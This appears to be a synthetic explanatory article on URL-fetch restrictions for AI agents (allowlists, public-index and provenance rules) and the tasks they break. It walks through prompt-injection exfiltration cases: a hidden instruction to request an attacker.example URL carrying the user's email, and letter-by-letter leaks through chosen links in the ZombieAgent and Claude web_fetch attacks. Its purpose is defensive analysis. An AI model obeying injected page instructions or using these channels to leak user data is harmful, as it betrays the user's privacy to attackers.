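# Web tasks that URL restrictions on AI agents break, and the confirmation prompts used instead

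## Why AI agents are limited in which web addresses they may fetch

An AI agent is a language model connected to tools that let it open web pages, run searches or send requests to other services on a person's behalf. To read a page, the agent's software requests the page's URL, the full web address, as a browser does when someone clicks a link. OpenAI's ChatGPT and Anthropic's Claude both work this way, and both companies restrict which URLs the model may request on its own. This is because requesting a page also sends information to whoever runs the site, and an attacker who can influence the agent can influence what is sent. The restrictions also block harmless tasks, such as looking up a train, and the user may then have to approve the request by hand.

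### What a URL transmits

Consider an invented address, `trains.example/search?from=Leeds&to=York`. The standard for the syntax of such addresses, the RFC Editor's *Uniform Resource Identifier (URI)*, has a name for each piece. In front of the address stands the scheme, usually "https". Then comes the host, `trains.example`, which identifies the site. The path, `/search`, points to a page or function within the site, and everything after the question mark is the query. This query carries two parameters, a city of departure and a city of arrival. (A URL may also end in a fragment, marked by a hash sign, which browsers use locally and do not send.)

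The site's server receives the path and the query in full, since it needs them to find the right page. Encryption hides them from eavesdroppers but not from the site. Sites' analytics and server logs also commonly record the URLs that visitors request, as OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) notes.

A train search has to include cities and dates in the URL, but URL parameters can carry any text, including an email address or the title of a private document. The path can carry such text too. The server receives it with the request, even if the page then fails to load.

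### Prompt injection and URL exfiltration

In a prompt injection attack, someone hides instructions in content that an AI system reads, to make it act against its user. OpenAI gives the example of a page designed to make the model fetch `attacker.example/collect?data=<something private>`. A user might ask an agent to summarise an article that contains a hidden instruction, perhaps invisible to human readers, to fetch this address with the user's email address in place of the bracketed words. If the model complies, its browsing tool requests the completed URL, and the attacker reads the email address in the server's log. The user may see nothing, because the request can happen in the background, for example when the software loads an image or previews a link. This attack is an example of URL exfiltration, which means leaking data by placing it in, or signalling it through, the URLs an agent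 requests.

The model may follow such instructions because the user's request, the developer's instructions and the contents of the web page all arrive in one context window, the text the model works from. Nothing in that window reliably separates commands from other text. Security researchers call this general pattern a "confused deputy", in which a party without some authority induces a program that legitimately holds it to misuse it. Here, that authority is the ability to send web requests.

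The problem is about as old as chat assistants. *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, a post on the security blog Embrace The Red, describes how the blogger told OpenAI in early 2023 about a leak of this type in ChatGPT that required no click from the user. Microsoft fixed the same flaw in Bing Chat that May by generally preventing the chat from loading images. OpenAI added a first check on URLs in December 2023 without explaining how the check decided that a URL was safe, and the blogger found ways around it over the following years.

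*Silent Egress* (Lan, Kaul and colleagues, 2026) measured how often an agent follows an instruction in a web page to send out a secret, using a test system at eBay. The agent automatically fetched a preview of any URL it met. The researchers placed an invented secret in its context and gave it the same harmless request every time, to summarise a page. The page contained an instruction to send the secret to a server whose traffic they recorded. They varied where the instruction appeared on the page (title, description metadata, body text or link text), whether the agent reached the page directly or through redirects, and whether the instruction was to send the secret whole or in four separate fragments. They ran each of the 16 resulting set-ups 30 times.

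At least one request reached the attacker's server in 423 of the 480 runs (88.1%). Attacks that asked for the secret in one piece succeeded in 238 of 240 runs, summed across the individual set-ups. Attacks that split the secret succeeded in 185 of 240, though some of those runs delivered only part of it. In 95% of the successful attacks, the agent's written answer looked normal, so a reviewer who checked only the answers would have missed nearly all of them. In 120 control runs with harmless pages, the agent never contacted the attacker's server.

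The 88% is not an estimate for commercial assistants. Lan and colleagues tested a single small open model, qwen2.5:7b, put the secret in plain view and gave the model almost no safety instructions. They describe this set-up as favourable to the attacker. They also suggest that stronger models might do worse, because a model that follows instructions better may also follow injected ones better, but they did not test a stronger model.

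The same paper also compared defences on one set-up, again with 30 runs per condition. A system prompt (the developer's standing instructions to the model) that told the model to treat web content as data lowered the leak rate from 100% to 66.7%. Tagging the page's text as untrusted made no difference. A check outside the model, which allowed requests to only four listed domains, stopped every leak, even though the model tried to send the secret in all 30 runs. This was an easy test for the list, since no sensible list would include the attacker's domain. But the check should work for other models too, because it runs in the software that sends the request and works the same way whether or not the model follows the injected instructions.

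### Three rules for deciding which URLs to fetch

A domain allowlist is a list of sites an agent may contact. Developers who build on Claude can set one for its web fetch tool, which retrieves pages. According to an earlier edition of Anthropic's *Web fetch tool* documentation, an entry for `example.com` also covers subdomains such as `docs.example.com`, and a developer can narrow an entry to one part of a site, such as `example.com/blog`. Within those bounds, the list doesn't restrict the path or the parameters, so on its own it allows an agent to compose any address there, including one that contains private data.

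OpenAI gives two reasons for not relying on a list of trusted sites. First, many reputable sites offer redirects, which forward a visitor to a different address, so a request can begin at a trusted domain and end at the attacker's. Second, people visit far more than a handful of well-known sites, so a strict list would constantly interrupt them with warnings about harmless ones.

OpenAI's own solution, which it described in January 2026, is a public-index rule under which the agent may fetch a URL automatically only if an independent crawler has already seen that exact URL. A crawler is a program that visits public web pages and records the addresses it finds, as search engines do. OpenAI's crawler has no access to users' conversations or accounts, so an address in its index is unlikely to contain something a particular user told ChatGPT. A URL on a well-known domain still fails the check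 if the rest of the address is new. OpenAI treats a URL that fails as unverified, and either steers the agent away from it or asks the user about it. Embrace The Red's understanding is that ChatGPT also accepts a URL that the user has typed into the conversation. OpenAI's *Designing agents to resist prompt injection* calls the safeguard Safe Url and says it also applies to page visits in Atlas, the company's browser, and to searches and page visits in its Deep Research feature.

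Under Anthropic's provenance rule, an agent may fetch only URLs that came from an approved source. The English documentation, *Web fetch tool*, states that Claude may not "dynamically construct URLs", meaning that it may not compose a URL itself instead of copying it whole from a source. The approved sources are the user's messages, the results of tools that the developer runs, and the results of earlier web searches and fetches. However, Willison (2026), a software developer, reports that Claude's fetch tool no longer follows links found inside pages it has fetched. *網頁擷取工具*, a newer Chinese edition of the documentation, excludes URLs that appear only in Claude's own output, only in the system prompt, or only in the results of certain other tools that Anthropic hosts, such as code execution.

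That edition adds a content check, under which the tool refuses a URL that appears to contain a password or an access key, unless the same credential appears in the system prompt or in the text of a user's message. The edition also describes a gap. If a developer's own tool runs code that Claude wrote, and the code prints a URL, the URL now counts as a tool result and becomes eligible, even though Claude composed it. Developers can close the gap with a setting that excludes particular tools as sources of eligible URLs, but those tools are included by default.

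Early on, Willison (2025) complained mildly that the approved sources were too broad. When he looked at the tool that September, he had hoped it would accept only URLs from the user's own prompts. That rule would be stricter, but it would also stop the agent from opening its search results, leaving it of little use for research.

### The same requests under each rule

Suppose a user is planning a trip from Leeds to York and asks an agent about rail strikes and train times. A web search returns a news article for the agent to open. To find train times, the agent builds a booking-site address from the two city names. It also reads a hostile page containing an instruction to send the user's email address to `attacker.example`.

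| Request | Domain allowlist | Public-index rule | Provenance rule |
|---|---|---|---|
| News link from the search results: `news.example/rail-strike-dates` | Fetched if `news.example` is on the list | Fetched if the crawler has recorded this URL | Fetched, because a search returned it |
| Train search composed by the agent: `trains.example/search?from=Leeds&to=York` | Fetched if `trains.example` is on the list | Unverified, unless the crawler happens to have recorded this exact URL | Refused |
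| Leak requested by the hostile page: `attacker.example/collect?data=` followed by the user's email address | Refused, because the site is not on the list | Unverified | Refused |

The news link generally passes, though the crawler may not have reached an article published minutes ago. The public-index rule and the provenance rule treat the other two requests, the train search and the leak, the same way. Both rules depend on where a URL came from, and neither address existed anywhere before the model wrote it.

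Inspecting the URL's contents would not distinguish the train search from the leak either, because both pass on something the user said in the conversation. The difference is that the user wants the booking site to know where they are going, and the URL does not show what the user wants. The allowlist does treat the two requests differently if somebody has already added `trains.example` to it, but only because of that entry, so it would also allow a request that sent the email address to `trains.example`.

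A block or prompt triggered by a harmless request is a false alarm. Under the two rules about origin, a harmless train search with a new address triggers one by design. If a rule stops all constructed URLs, the share of stops that are false alarms equals the share of constructed URLs that are harmless. Suppose, for illustration, that one constructed URL in 10,000 leaks something. Then 9,999 of every 10,000 stops are false alarms. OpenAI describes the cases in which Safe Url intervenes as "rare", which may well be true as a share of all the pages its agents open, but nearly all of those cases could still be false alarms.

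Lan and colleagues report a "false positive rate" of zero, by which they mean that the agent sent nothing to the attacker when there was no attack. They did not measure how many harmless requests their defences blocked, and some of their filters would probably have blocked quite a few. One rejected any URL whose path contained "collect", which, taken literally, would also block a museum's "collections" page. Another looked for "auth", which also occurs in "author". Both filters stopped every leak that reached them in the experiment, but in a test made up only of attacks, a rule that blocked every request would have scored just as well.

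### What a permitted fetch does not guarantee

OpenAI claims only that the agent should not quietly leak a user's data through the URL itself, not that the page behind a permitted URL is accurate or free of harmful instructions. A crawler records that an address exists but does not verify the page's content, and whoever runs the site can change the page later. A fabricated news story on a public site therefore passes the public-index rule, and also the provenance rule if it turns up in a search. The agent may then repeat the story to the user as fact.

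An agent under these rules can still read a prompt injection, as in the example above, where it had permission to read the hostile page. The rules apply only later, when the model tries to send information out by requesting a URL. An agent that can also send email or edit files needs separate controls on those actions.

The rules reduce leaks through web addresses but do not rule them out. Anthropic warns developers of a "residual risk" and advises those who handle sensitive data alongside untrusted content to add a domain allowlist, cap the number of fetches or switch the fetch tool off. One reason for the remaining risk is that an agent can reveal information by which existing addresses it chooses to fetch, without composing a new one. The blog Embrace The Red considers small leaks of this kind still feasible against OpenAI's index. It also points out that a check protects only the products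 that include it. For some time after OpenAI added its first safeguard to ChatGPT, the company's macOS and iOS apps did not have it.

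## Following links found inside a page

To finish a task, an agent often needs to follow a link on a page it has fetched, such as a link to the second page of a list, the study an article cites or a file to download. This looks like one of the safest requests an agent can make, because the model copies the URL exactly. If the model isn't allowed to change the URL, a hostile page can't get it to add the user's email address.

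The site's owner can see which link the agent opened. If a page offers many links and gets the agent to choose one based on private information, the choice reveals that information. Security researchers have done this to ChatGPT and Claude, and OpenAI and Anthropic responded by blocking their assistants from following certain links.

### How much a choice of link reveals

Suppose a hostile page contains 26 links, one for each letter, and an instruction to open the link for the first letter of the user's surname. The agent requests that link exactly as it appears on the page. The site's owner sees the request in the server log and learns the letter. The linked page can then contain 26 more links for the second letter.

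Information theory measures messages like this in bits. The answer to a yes/no question carries one bit if both answers are equally likely, and a choice among k equally likely options carries log₂(k) bits. A choice among 26 links therefore carries log₂(26), or about 4.7 bits. The bits from successive choices add up, so six choices carry about 28 bits. That is enough to distinguish all 26⁶ (about 309 million) six-letter strings, including every possible six-letter name. A seventh choice raises the number of strings to about 8 billion, roughly the number of people alive.

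An attacker can learn about a user from the agent's choice of link alone. For example, the attacker could create a page that links to articles on 16 illnesses and tell the agent to open the one most relevant to its user, which would reveal up to four bits in one request. Even a single link can reveal one bit if the agent opens it only when some statement about the user is true.

*Actions Speak Louder than Words* (2026) measured how reliably an agent's choice of link can leak information to an attacker. In a test with four candidate answers, or two bits per choice, the page triggered a request in 98.7% of trials, and the researchers recovered the answer with 93.8% accuracy. They also describe signals in the number, order, timing and size of an agent's requests, but found that the choice of link gave an attacker the best balance of capacity, reliability and cost.

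### OpenAI's limit on links in emails

The attack on ChatGPT grew out of an earlier one that did use constructed URLs. In 2025 Radware, a cybersecurity company, showed that an email with hidden instructions could make ChatGPT's Deep Research feature put an employee's name and address into a URL on an attacker's server. Radware called this ShadowLeak and reported it on 18 June. OpenAI said by early August that it had fixed the flaw, according to The Record's *OpenAI fixes zero-click ShadowLeak vulnerability affecting ChatGPT Deep Research agent*. After the fix, ChatGPT opened URLs only exactly as given and would not add parameters even when told to.

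*ZombieAgent* describes how Radware researcher Zvika Babo got around this. His email contained a ready-made link for each letter and digit, and one for a space. When the user later asked ChatGPT to do something with their Gmail account, it read the email and opened the links one after another to spell out private data. To preserve the order of the characters, Babo made a separate set of links for each position, so "a" as the first character had a different address from "a" as the second.

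Radware reported the attack to OpenAI on 26 September 2025. Three days later it sent an improved version for which it claimed a 100% success rate, though it does not give the number of trials. OpenAI fixed the flaw on 16 December, and Radware published its report on 8 January 2026, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *New Zero-Click Attack Lets ChatGPT User Steal Data*.

Since the fix, ChatGPT no longer opens a link that comes from an email unless the user has supplied it directly, according to *ZombieAgent*, an article on the Italian technology news site Punto Informatico. The article adds that this blocks only one specific attack. Radware had also leaked data through instructions in a shared file, and it warns that any service connected to ChatGPT, such as Google Drive or GitHub, could supply the instructions. A limit on email links alone would not cover those routes. The public-index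 rule, which OpenAI described six weeks after the fix, applies to links from any source. It is unclear how the two rules combine when an email contains a link that OpenAI's crawler has already recorded.

### The July 2026 report on Claude

Willison (2026), in *How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets*, describes a similar hole that Ayush Paul found in Claude's web_fetch tool. The provenance rule then let the tool open links inside pages it had already fetched. Claude's chat assistant also had private information to leak, because it can draw on a memory of the user's past conversations.

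Paul built a website with instructions for Claude to find the user's profile by working through the alphabet. Each page offered links that extended the address by one letter, and the server generated the next page when Claude reached it. Claude didn't compose any of these addresses, so the rule allowed them all. The site showed its hostile version only to visitors that identified themselves as Claude, so a person who opened the same page would have seen nothing wrong.

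Paul extracted the user's name, home city and employer. The blogger dyb adds in *The Read-Only Lie* that Paul had never told Claude his home city. Claude had inferred it from the name of a high-school hackathon. An attack like this can therefore leak what the model infers about a person as well as what the person typed. Each page had 27 links, one for each letter and one for a hyphen, so each choice of link carried about 4.75 bits. By dyb's rough estimate, the attack took 30 fetches, or about 143 bits in total.

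Anthropic did not pay Paul a bounty, saying that it had already identified the problem internally. It then stopped the tool from opening links found in fetched pages. In the chat assistant, the tool can now open only URLs that the user entered or a web search returned.

It is less clear whether the fix also covers the API, which developers use to build Claude into their own software. Willison's account concerns the ordinary chat assistant. A June 2026 copy of Anthropic's English API documentation allows URLs from earlier fetches, but it predates Paul's report. A copy of the Japanese documentation from 11 August, a month after the report, still allows them.

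The API may no longer follow such links, because the Japanese text may be older than the fix. The newest tool version it describes dates from March. But nothing in Anthropic's documentation suggests that the fix protects developers who use the API. Those who handle private data should assume it doesn't until they have tested it, for example by asking Claude to fetch a page on their own server that links to a second page there, and then checking the server's log for a request for the second page.

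### What stops working

The table's entries are deduced by applying the published rules to six ordinary tasks, and actual products may behave differently. In every case the user can also paste the link into the chat, since both companies treat a URL in the user's message as approved.

| Task | Claude's chat assistant since the fix | ChatGPT | Workaround |
|---|---|---|---|
| Next page of a list | Refused | Opened if the crawler has recorded that page | Paste links to several pages at once |
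| Chapter listed on a documentation contents page | Refused, unless a search returns it | Usually opened, if the documentation is public | Ask the agent to search for the chapter by title |
| Source cited in an article | Refused, unless a search returns it | Opened if the crawler has recorded it | Ask the agent to search by title and author |
| PDF behind a landing page | Refused, unless a search returns the PDF itself | Opened if the PDF has a fixed public address | Download the file and upload it to the chat |
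| Redirect to another address | Depends on whether the software follows it automatically | Depends on how the software checks the destination | Open the link in a browser and paste the final address |
| Link in an email | Refused | Refused, unless the user supplies it | Paste the link, or the text of the page behind it |

URL restrictions cause the most trouble with lists that span several pages. A search engine will seldom return page seven of a shop's results, and the model can't change the 6 in page six's address to a 7, because that would be a constructed URL. The user can paste links to pages two to ten in one message, but only after finding them, which is much of the work they wanted the agent to do.

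The loss is easier to miss when the blocked link leads to a cited source. An agent that can't open a study may still describe it from the article that cites it. If the article misreports the study, the agent repeats the error, and the user may assume that the agent checked the original.

Redirects are a special case because the site's server, not the model, picks the destination. The server can pass on only what it already received, so following a redirect automatically leaks nothing through the choice of links, though it may carry whatever was in the first URL to a second site. If the software instead returns the new address to the model, the address counts as one found in a fetched page, and Claude's chat assistant would refuse to fetch it.

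Some of these tasks failed even before the fix. According to Anthropic's API documentation, the fetch tool does not support pages that JavaScript builds in the browser, which rules out many lists with a "load more" button. It also rejects URLs longer than 250 characters, and short-lived download links often exceed that limit.

### Whether search can replace the link

An agent may not need the link if it can search for the page instead. According to Anthropic's API documentation, if a user asks for the README file (the introductory page) of a named software project without giving its address, Claude searches for the page and then fetches the result. For a well-known public page, this adds little more than one extra search.

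Searching for a page fails when the search engine has not indexed it. An announcement published minutes ago may not be indexed yet, and some pages never are because few other sites link to them. Private pages, such as a parcel-tracking page or a document shared with anyone who has the link, should never appear in search results. Links people receive by email often lead to private pages like these, so search is least useful where OpenAI's limit applies.

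Some failures of this kind would happen even without the fix. Site owners can ask automated visitors to stay away from certain pages in a file called robots.txt, and Anthropic's tool refuses some URLs for that reason. If a page is missing from search for the same reason, the agent could not have opened it by following a link either.

A search may also return a different page from the one the original link led to, and the agent may not notice. For example, a search for a chapter of a software manual can return the same chapter from an older release, and a search for a study can return a press article about it.

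Search doesn't fully close the leak either, because an agent also chooses which results to open. An attacker could publish a page for each letter, wait for search engines to index them, and then get the agent to search for the pages that spell out the data, in order. Neither Paul nor Radware demonstrated this, and it would be slower than following links. But the attacker may not need new pages. In discussing OpenAI's index, Embrace The Red points out that any larger blog probably already has 36 indexed pages, enough for 26 letters and ten digits.

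### Caps and no-repeat rules

A vendor could allow link-following but limit it, for example by capping the number of links an agent may follow or by stopping it from requesting the same URL twice.

If an agent may follow n links and each page offers k of them, its choices can leak at most n × log₂(k) bits. Halving the number of links followed halves this maximum, while halving the number offered on each page removes only one bit per choice. An attacker can therefore make up for a tight cap on links followed by offering more links per page, as the third row of the next table shows. The figures exclude signals other than the choice of links, such as timing.

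| Limit | Links the site offers | Most that can leak |
|---|---|---|
| None, and the agent follows six links | 26 per page | 28.2 bits |
| Cap of three links | 26 per page | 14.1 bits |
| Cap of three links | 1,000 per page | 29.9 bits |
| Cap of one link | 1,000 on one page | 10.0 bits |
| No repeats, and the agent follows six links | The same 26 each time | 27.3 bits |
| No repeats, six links, and the attacker can't tell their order | The same 26 each time | 17.8 bits |
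| No repeats, and the agent follows six links | A new set of 26 for each position | 28.2 bits |

Anthropic's API lets developers cap the number of fetches but sets no default cap. The sample code in its documentation uses a cap of five. Fetching the hostile page uses one, leaving four link choices, which can carry 18.8 bits if each page has 26 links. According to dyb, spelling "ayush-paul" on Paul's site took ten choices. A cap of ten fetches would have left nine, enough for all but the last letter.

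Anthropic's cap also applies to each API request separately, so a long conversation can get a new allowance with every message. Radware's attack shows how an attacker could exploit this. In one version, instructions that Babo had stored in ChatGPT's memory made it read the attacker's email and leak data before answering each new message. A cap on each conversation would have slowed that leak without ending it. A cap low enough to make much difference would also stop an agent from comparing a dozen products for its user.

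A no-repeat rule disrupts honest users much less, since an agent seldom needs to load the same page twice. Embrace The Red suggests either refusing the second visit or storing the first response for a few minutes and reusing it. Anthropic's fetch tool already stores responses by default, mainly for speed, though developers can switch this off. Embrace The Red expects some leakage to remain under either version, and the table suggests that most of it would. With 26 fixed links, the rule removes less than one bit from a six-letter message, although a name with a repeated letter would need a second set of links. Neither attack described above depended on repeated URLs, since Babo's links differed by position and Paul's addresses grew longer at every step.

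The public-index rule also limits these attacks because the attacker has to get every page into the index beforehand. Paul's design would need a separate page for every possible sequence of letters, or about 321 million pages to cover names of up to six letters. No crawler is likely to record that many, so the rule would block this design. Babo's design needs only one page per letter and position, or 156 pages for six letters, so it would still be feasible for a patient attacker.

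Vendors could also use an alarm, proposed by dyb, that triggers when an agent rapidly fetches a series of addresses on one site, each one character longer than the last. Ordinary browsing would rarely trigger it, and it would have caught Paul's attack before the attack finished spelling his name. However, it would miss Babo's links, because their addresses do not get longer.

An attack may leak less than these maximums, because the model has to carry out every step correctly. The small model that Lan and colleagues tested leaked a secret less reliably in fragments than in one piece. Radware claims a 100% success rate against ChatGPT, which suggests that commercial assistants may not be this unreliable.

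How much a cap helps also depends on the length of the secret. Leaking a random 128-bit access key takes 28 choices among 26 links, so a cap of five fetches would protect most of it. The same cap would not protect the answer to a yes/no question, such as whether the user is looking for a new job, because the agent can reveal it by opening a single link.

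## Building search and booking addresses from a user's details

An agent can follow a link by copying its address, but to run a search or start a booking, it usually has to write an address that includes something about the user. OpenAI's help page *ChatGPT generated links* gives the example of a user who asks where to find cars to buy nearby. ChatGPT has the user's home city, London, so it might answer with a link to `example.com/car_search/London`. The link could help the user find a car, but OpenAI points out that opening it also reveals to the car-search service where the user lives.

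The city is in the path here, so a filter that checked only the query would miss it.

### When a useful URL and a leak look the same

An attacker can ask for an address of the same form as the useful one:

- `cars.example/car_search/London`
- `attacker.example/car_search/London`

The addresses differ only in the host, and even the host wouldn't reveal the attack if the attacker's site had an innocent-looking name. In some cases the host is the same too. Suppose a car dealer wants to know where visitors live, and hides an instruction on its own site to open the search page for the user's home city. A user who lives in London asks an agent to summarise the dealer's article about winter tyres. If the agent obeys the hidden instruction, it requests `cars.example/car_search/London`, the same address it would request for a user who wanted to buy a car there.

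The model composed both requests, and they are identical except for what the user wanted, so any rule based on the URL or its origin gets one of them wrong.

Contextual integrity, a related idea from privacy research, judges a flow of information by the norms of the setting in which it takes place. *SPILLage* (Roh, Bagdasarian and colleagues, 2026) explains that the judgement depends on who sends the information, who receives it, whom it is about, what type of information it is and on what terms it is passed on. A URL identifies the recipient and contains the information, but it doesn't show the terms or whether London is the user's home or the city where the user's daughter wants a car.

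In an example from Roh and colleagues, a user asks an agent to find affordable glucose test strips on Amazon. The user's emails and chats reveal type 2 diabetes, a divorce and an income of $1,000 a month. The researchers class the diabetes as relevant to the task, and the divorce and income as irrelevant. An agent could search for "glucose test strips" or for "glucose test strips for recently divorced women". The two search URLs would have the same form, but the second would contain a longer phrase.

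Even people who know the whole request may disagree about which details belong in it. The user asked for affordable strips, so the income is arguably relevant, at least as a reason to set a price limit.

### Why no index can hold these addresses

A crawler can't solve the problem by collecting useful search addresses in advance, because there are too many. As an illustration, imagine a hotel site that covers 1,000 cities and accepts 365 arrival dates, 14 lengths of stay and four party sizes. The number of possible searches is

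1,000 × 365 × 14 × 4 = 20,440,000.

At one address per second, a crawler would need about 237 days to record all the addresses, and by then almost two thirds of the arrival dates would have passed. Each new day would add 56,000 addresses. If the site also put the user's currency, chosen from 20 options, in the URL, the total would rise to about 409 million.

A crawler would not normally find most of these addresses, because it discovers pages largely by following links, and a search form doesn't link to every result it could produce. Many site owners also ask crawlers to stay out of their search results.

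A complete index could let the agent leak data through its choice of address. If an attacker's site had 20.44 million addresses in the index, a single permitted request could leak up to 24.3 bits, slightly more than five choices among 26 links.

Some constructed URLs will pass the public-index rule because the page already exists. A car site may well publish a page for each large city, in which case ChatGPT could open the London page without asking, even though this would reveal to the site where the user lives. Someone in a village without its own page would get a warning for the same kind of search. The difference is partly sensible, since naming a village narrows down who the user is far more than naming London does. But the index only records which addresses exist, so any match between the warnings and the sensitivity of the information is a coincidence.

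Google uses a similar rule for the AI agent in its Chrome browser. According to *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* (Parker, 2025), a fixed check restricts model-generated URLs to "known, public URLs". Parker doesn't explain how Google decides which URLs are known. If Google relies on an index, the same arithmetic applies.

### Links that broke in ChatGPT

Developers began to report broken links soon after OpenAI added its first URL check in December 2023. The reports below are historical, and most describe one developer's experience with a link ChatGPT showed to a user, not a page ChatGPT fetched itself. They still show how a check on constructed URLs affects ordinary tools.

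Many of the reports came from people building custom GPTs, versions of ChatGPT set up for a particular task. In *GPTs's link creation issue*, widztech (2024) wrote on 21 January that a link worked on its own but came out empty once it included a user ID in the query. In *Custom GPT Bug*, another thread on OpenAI's developer forum, a developer reported that links failed if anything followed the question mark. Someone else replied that their own links worked with tracking parameters. The question mark alone therefore can't explain the failures, and the cause isn't clear from the posts.

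OpenAI's answer, probably from early February 2024, described two "known edge cases": having the model construct a full URL and having it fill in details of a URL. OpenAI said developers should instead have their own server return the finished address. In *URLs served by action/GPT not clickable in desktop*, a developer objected that almost any request for a link would fall under these cases. The objection seems right for a search or booking tool, because filling in the details is the tool's main purpose.

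OpenAI's workaround satisfies the check, but the developer's server needs the city and dates to build a hotel search. The model has to send them to the server first, so the user's details still leave the conversation.

A user's experiments in *Make GPT return clickable links in chat* suggest that who wrote the URL affected whether the link worked. In one experiment, ChatGPT produced a working link when the user supplied the full URL, including the search term, but not when the user asked ChatGPT to add the term.

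The clearest example is a flashcard tool whose developer wanted ChatGPT to write questions and answers on any topic and put them into the tool's URL, so that the user could click the link and start studying. In *Can not open generated hyperlinks in desktop browser*, the developer reports that ChatGPT's safety check returned "safe: true" for the tool's bare address but "safe: false" for the same address with three questions added, one of them about the capital of Japan. Nothing in the address was private, but no crawler could have recorded every set of flashcards that a model might write.

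The post is undated, but its position on the forum suggests spring 2024. The developer was puzzled that the link worked in the mobile app and suspected a bug. The link probably worked because the iOS app did not yet have the check.

Another developer had the opposite problem, with links that worked on the web but not in the iPhone app. The undated post *Mobile app strips URL parameters when using window.openai.open* describes an app that runs inside ChatGPT and sends users to products on Google. In the iPhone app, the links kept the general search term but lost the product's catalogue number and the country. The app didn't have the exemption from ChatGPT's link warning that *Verifying URLs used in apps* describes, and the warning appeared on both platforms.

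The app may have removed the catalogue number as a deliberate safeguard, or it may have mishandled the colon and comma in it. The developer got around the problem by encoding the whole address in the path of a link to their own server, which then redirected the user to the product. If the app was removing parameters to prevent leaks, the workaround shows that this doesn't work, because the path can carry the same information.

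Removing parameters also makes mistakes harder to notice than blocking the link would. A hotel link that loses its dates may still open a page of rooms and prices for the site's default dates. The user could book the wrong night without seeing an error.

### Medical searches, birth dates and calendar entries

The useful addresses in the examples so far contained little that most people would mind sharing. The decision is harder when the site needs sensitive information to do what the user asked.

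To show a user glucose test strips, a pharmacy has to receive a search such as `pharmacy.example/search?q=glucose+test+strips`. The search term suggests that the user, or someone close to them, has diabetes. How much the pharmacy learns depends partly on which software sends the request. A simple fetch tool may send it from the vendor's servers without the user's login, so the pharmacy doesn't see whose search it is. A browser agent may send the same URL while the user is logged in, and the pharmacy can then add the search to an account with the user's name on it.

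Chrome's agent asks for confirmation before it opens certain sensitive sites, including some that handle personal medical information. Parker says the agent recognises these sites from a list. A list can include a hospital's patient portal, but it is less useful for a general shop or a search engine, where only the search term is sensitive.

Insurers generally need a driver's date of birth to price car insurance, so their quote forms ask for it. A user who asks for a quote from one named insurer presumably wants that insurer to have it. The user's wishes are less clear if they ask an agent to "find the cheapest cover", since the agent might send the date to ten companies, most of which the user may not have heard of. A date of birth and a full postcode together will often identify one person, and users can't change their date of birth after a leak as they could a password. A confirmation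 prompt seems easier to justify here than for a train search, even though both requests are probably harmless.

The insurer needs the date of birth, but it doesn't need it in the URL. Putting it there adds a separate risk, because the date may be saved in the browser's history and the site's logs.

Some calendar services accept links that open a new entry with the title, time and place filled in. An agent that has found a clinic appointment in the user's email could offer a link such as `calendar.example/new?title=Clinic&date=2026-11-03`. This URL looks suspicious under any rule about where a URL came from or what it contains, because it is new and includes health information. But blocking it protects the user from very little, since the recipient is the user's own calendar provider, which would store the same details if the user typed them in.

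Adding the calendar service to the allowlist would fix this false alarm, but it could also open a new leak. If the service also lets a link add guests, a hostile email could get the agent to put the attacker's address in an extra parameter of the link, and the service might send the attacker an invitation when the user saves the event.

### Typing into the site's own form

Perhaps the agent could avoid composing a URL by opening the site's public search page and typing into the form. The agent in OpenAI's Atlas browser can do this. It views pages, clicks and types inside the user's browser, according to OpenAI's *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025).

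But many forms produce the same URL that the agent would have written. Web forms usually send their contents using either the GET or the POST method. With GET, the browser adds the field contents to the URL, so typing "Leeds" and "York" into a train site's form can lead to `trains.example/search?from=Leeds&to=York`. With POST, the browser sends them in the body of the request rather than in the URL. Search forms often use GET, which lets people bookmark or share the results. Forms that ask for personal details more often use POST.

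The Safe Url check covers page visits in Atlas, but OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) doesn't say whether this includes visits caused by the agent submitting a form. If it does, the train search still goes through the check when the agent types the cities into a GET form. If the check covers only addresses that the model writes, typing the cities avoids it, although the train site receives the same request as it would from an address the model wrote.

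A check that examines only the URL would not detect an agent submitting a date of birth to an insurer through a POST form, because the date would not be in the address. It could block a harmless train search but allow a form full of personal details. Some pages also send text to the server as someone types it, for example to suggest search terms, so the information may leave before the browser opens a new page.

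An attacker could publish a page with a text box and an instruction to enter the user's email address. If the page's address is in a public index, a rule that allows indexed URLs would let the agent open it. Text typed into the box can also reveal far more than the few bits conveyed by a choice of link. Filling in forms is therefore a safe substitute for building URLs only if something else controls where the agent may type.

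For each task, Chrome is designed to decide which sites the agent may read and which it may also click and type on. The first version tracked only the sites where the agent could both read and act. A second model, the User Alignment Critic, reviews each action the agent proposes and can reject it if it doesn't serve the user's stated goal. The critic receives a description of the action but not the raw web page, so instructions on a hostile page can't reach it directly.

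On this account, Chrome could refuse to open a hotel search address that the model wrote, yet let the agent enter the same city and dates on the hotel's site, so the agent could still do the search. This also makes some sense for security, because the critic can compare the action with what the user asked for. But the critic is a model and can be wrong, and Parker gives no figures for how often it approves a leak or rejects a harmless search.

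Form-filling also has practical drawbacks. The agent has to find the right fields, fill them in and submit the form, and it can make a mistake at each step. Anthropic's web fetch tool only retrieves pages, so an agent with no other web tool can't use forms.

Roh and colleagues found that agents also share too much on ordinary sites, even when nobody attacks them. They gave agents 180 shopping tasks on Amazon and eBay, along with relevant and irrelevant details about an invented user. They tested two systems for operating a browser, each with three OpenAI models (gpt-4o, o3 and o4-mini), in 1,080 runs. Agents sometimes typed irrelevant details into the sites, but they revealed them about five times as often through clicks, scrolling and other navigation. For example, an agent might click a product labelled "Divorce Party" while shopping for something else.

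The experiment shows that a check on typed text alone would have missed most of the disclosures it counted. It doesn't show how often agents overshare in everyday use, because the researchers put irrelevant details into every task. They also relied on another model, gpt-4o-mini, to judge what a site could infer from the agent's behaviour, and the agents ran on models that are now fairly old.

Adding privacy instructions to the prompt didn't stop the agents from sharing irrelevant details, and in some cases they shared more. Removing those details before the agent started worked better and raised task success by up to 17.9%. An agent that was never given the user's marital status can't put it in a search box or a URL. This doesn't help with details the task needs, such as the date of birth for an insurance quote, so someone still has to decide which companies should receive them.

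## Calling APIs whose requests carry parameters

Many services publish the same information twice, as web pages for people and through an API for programs. An API (application programming interface) is a set of requests that a service accepts from other software. An invented weather API might answer this request with York's forecast for one day:

`api.weather.example/v1/forecast?city=York&date=2026-11-03`

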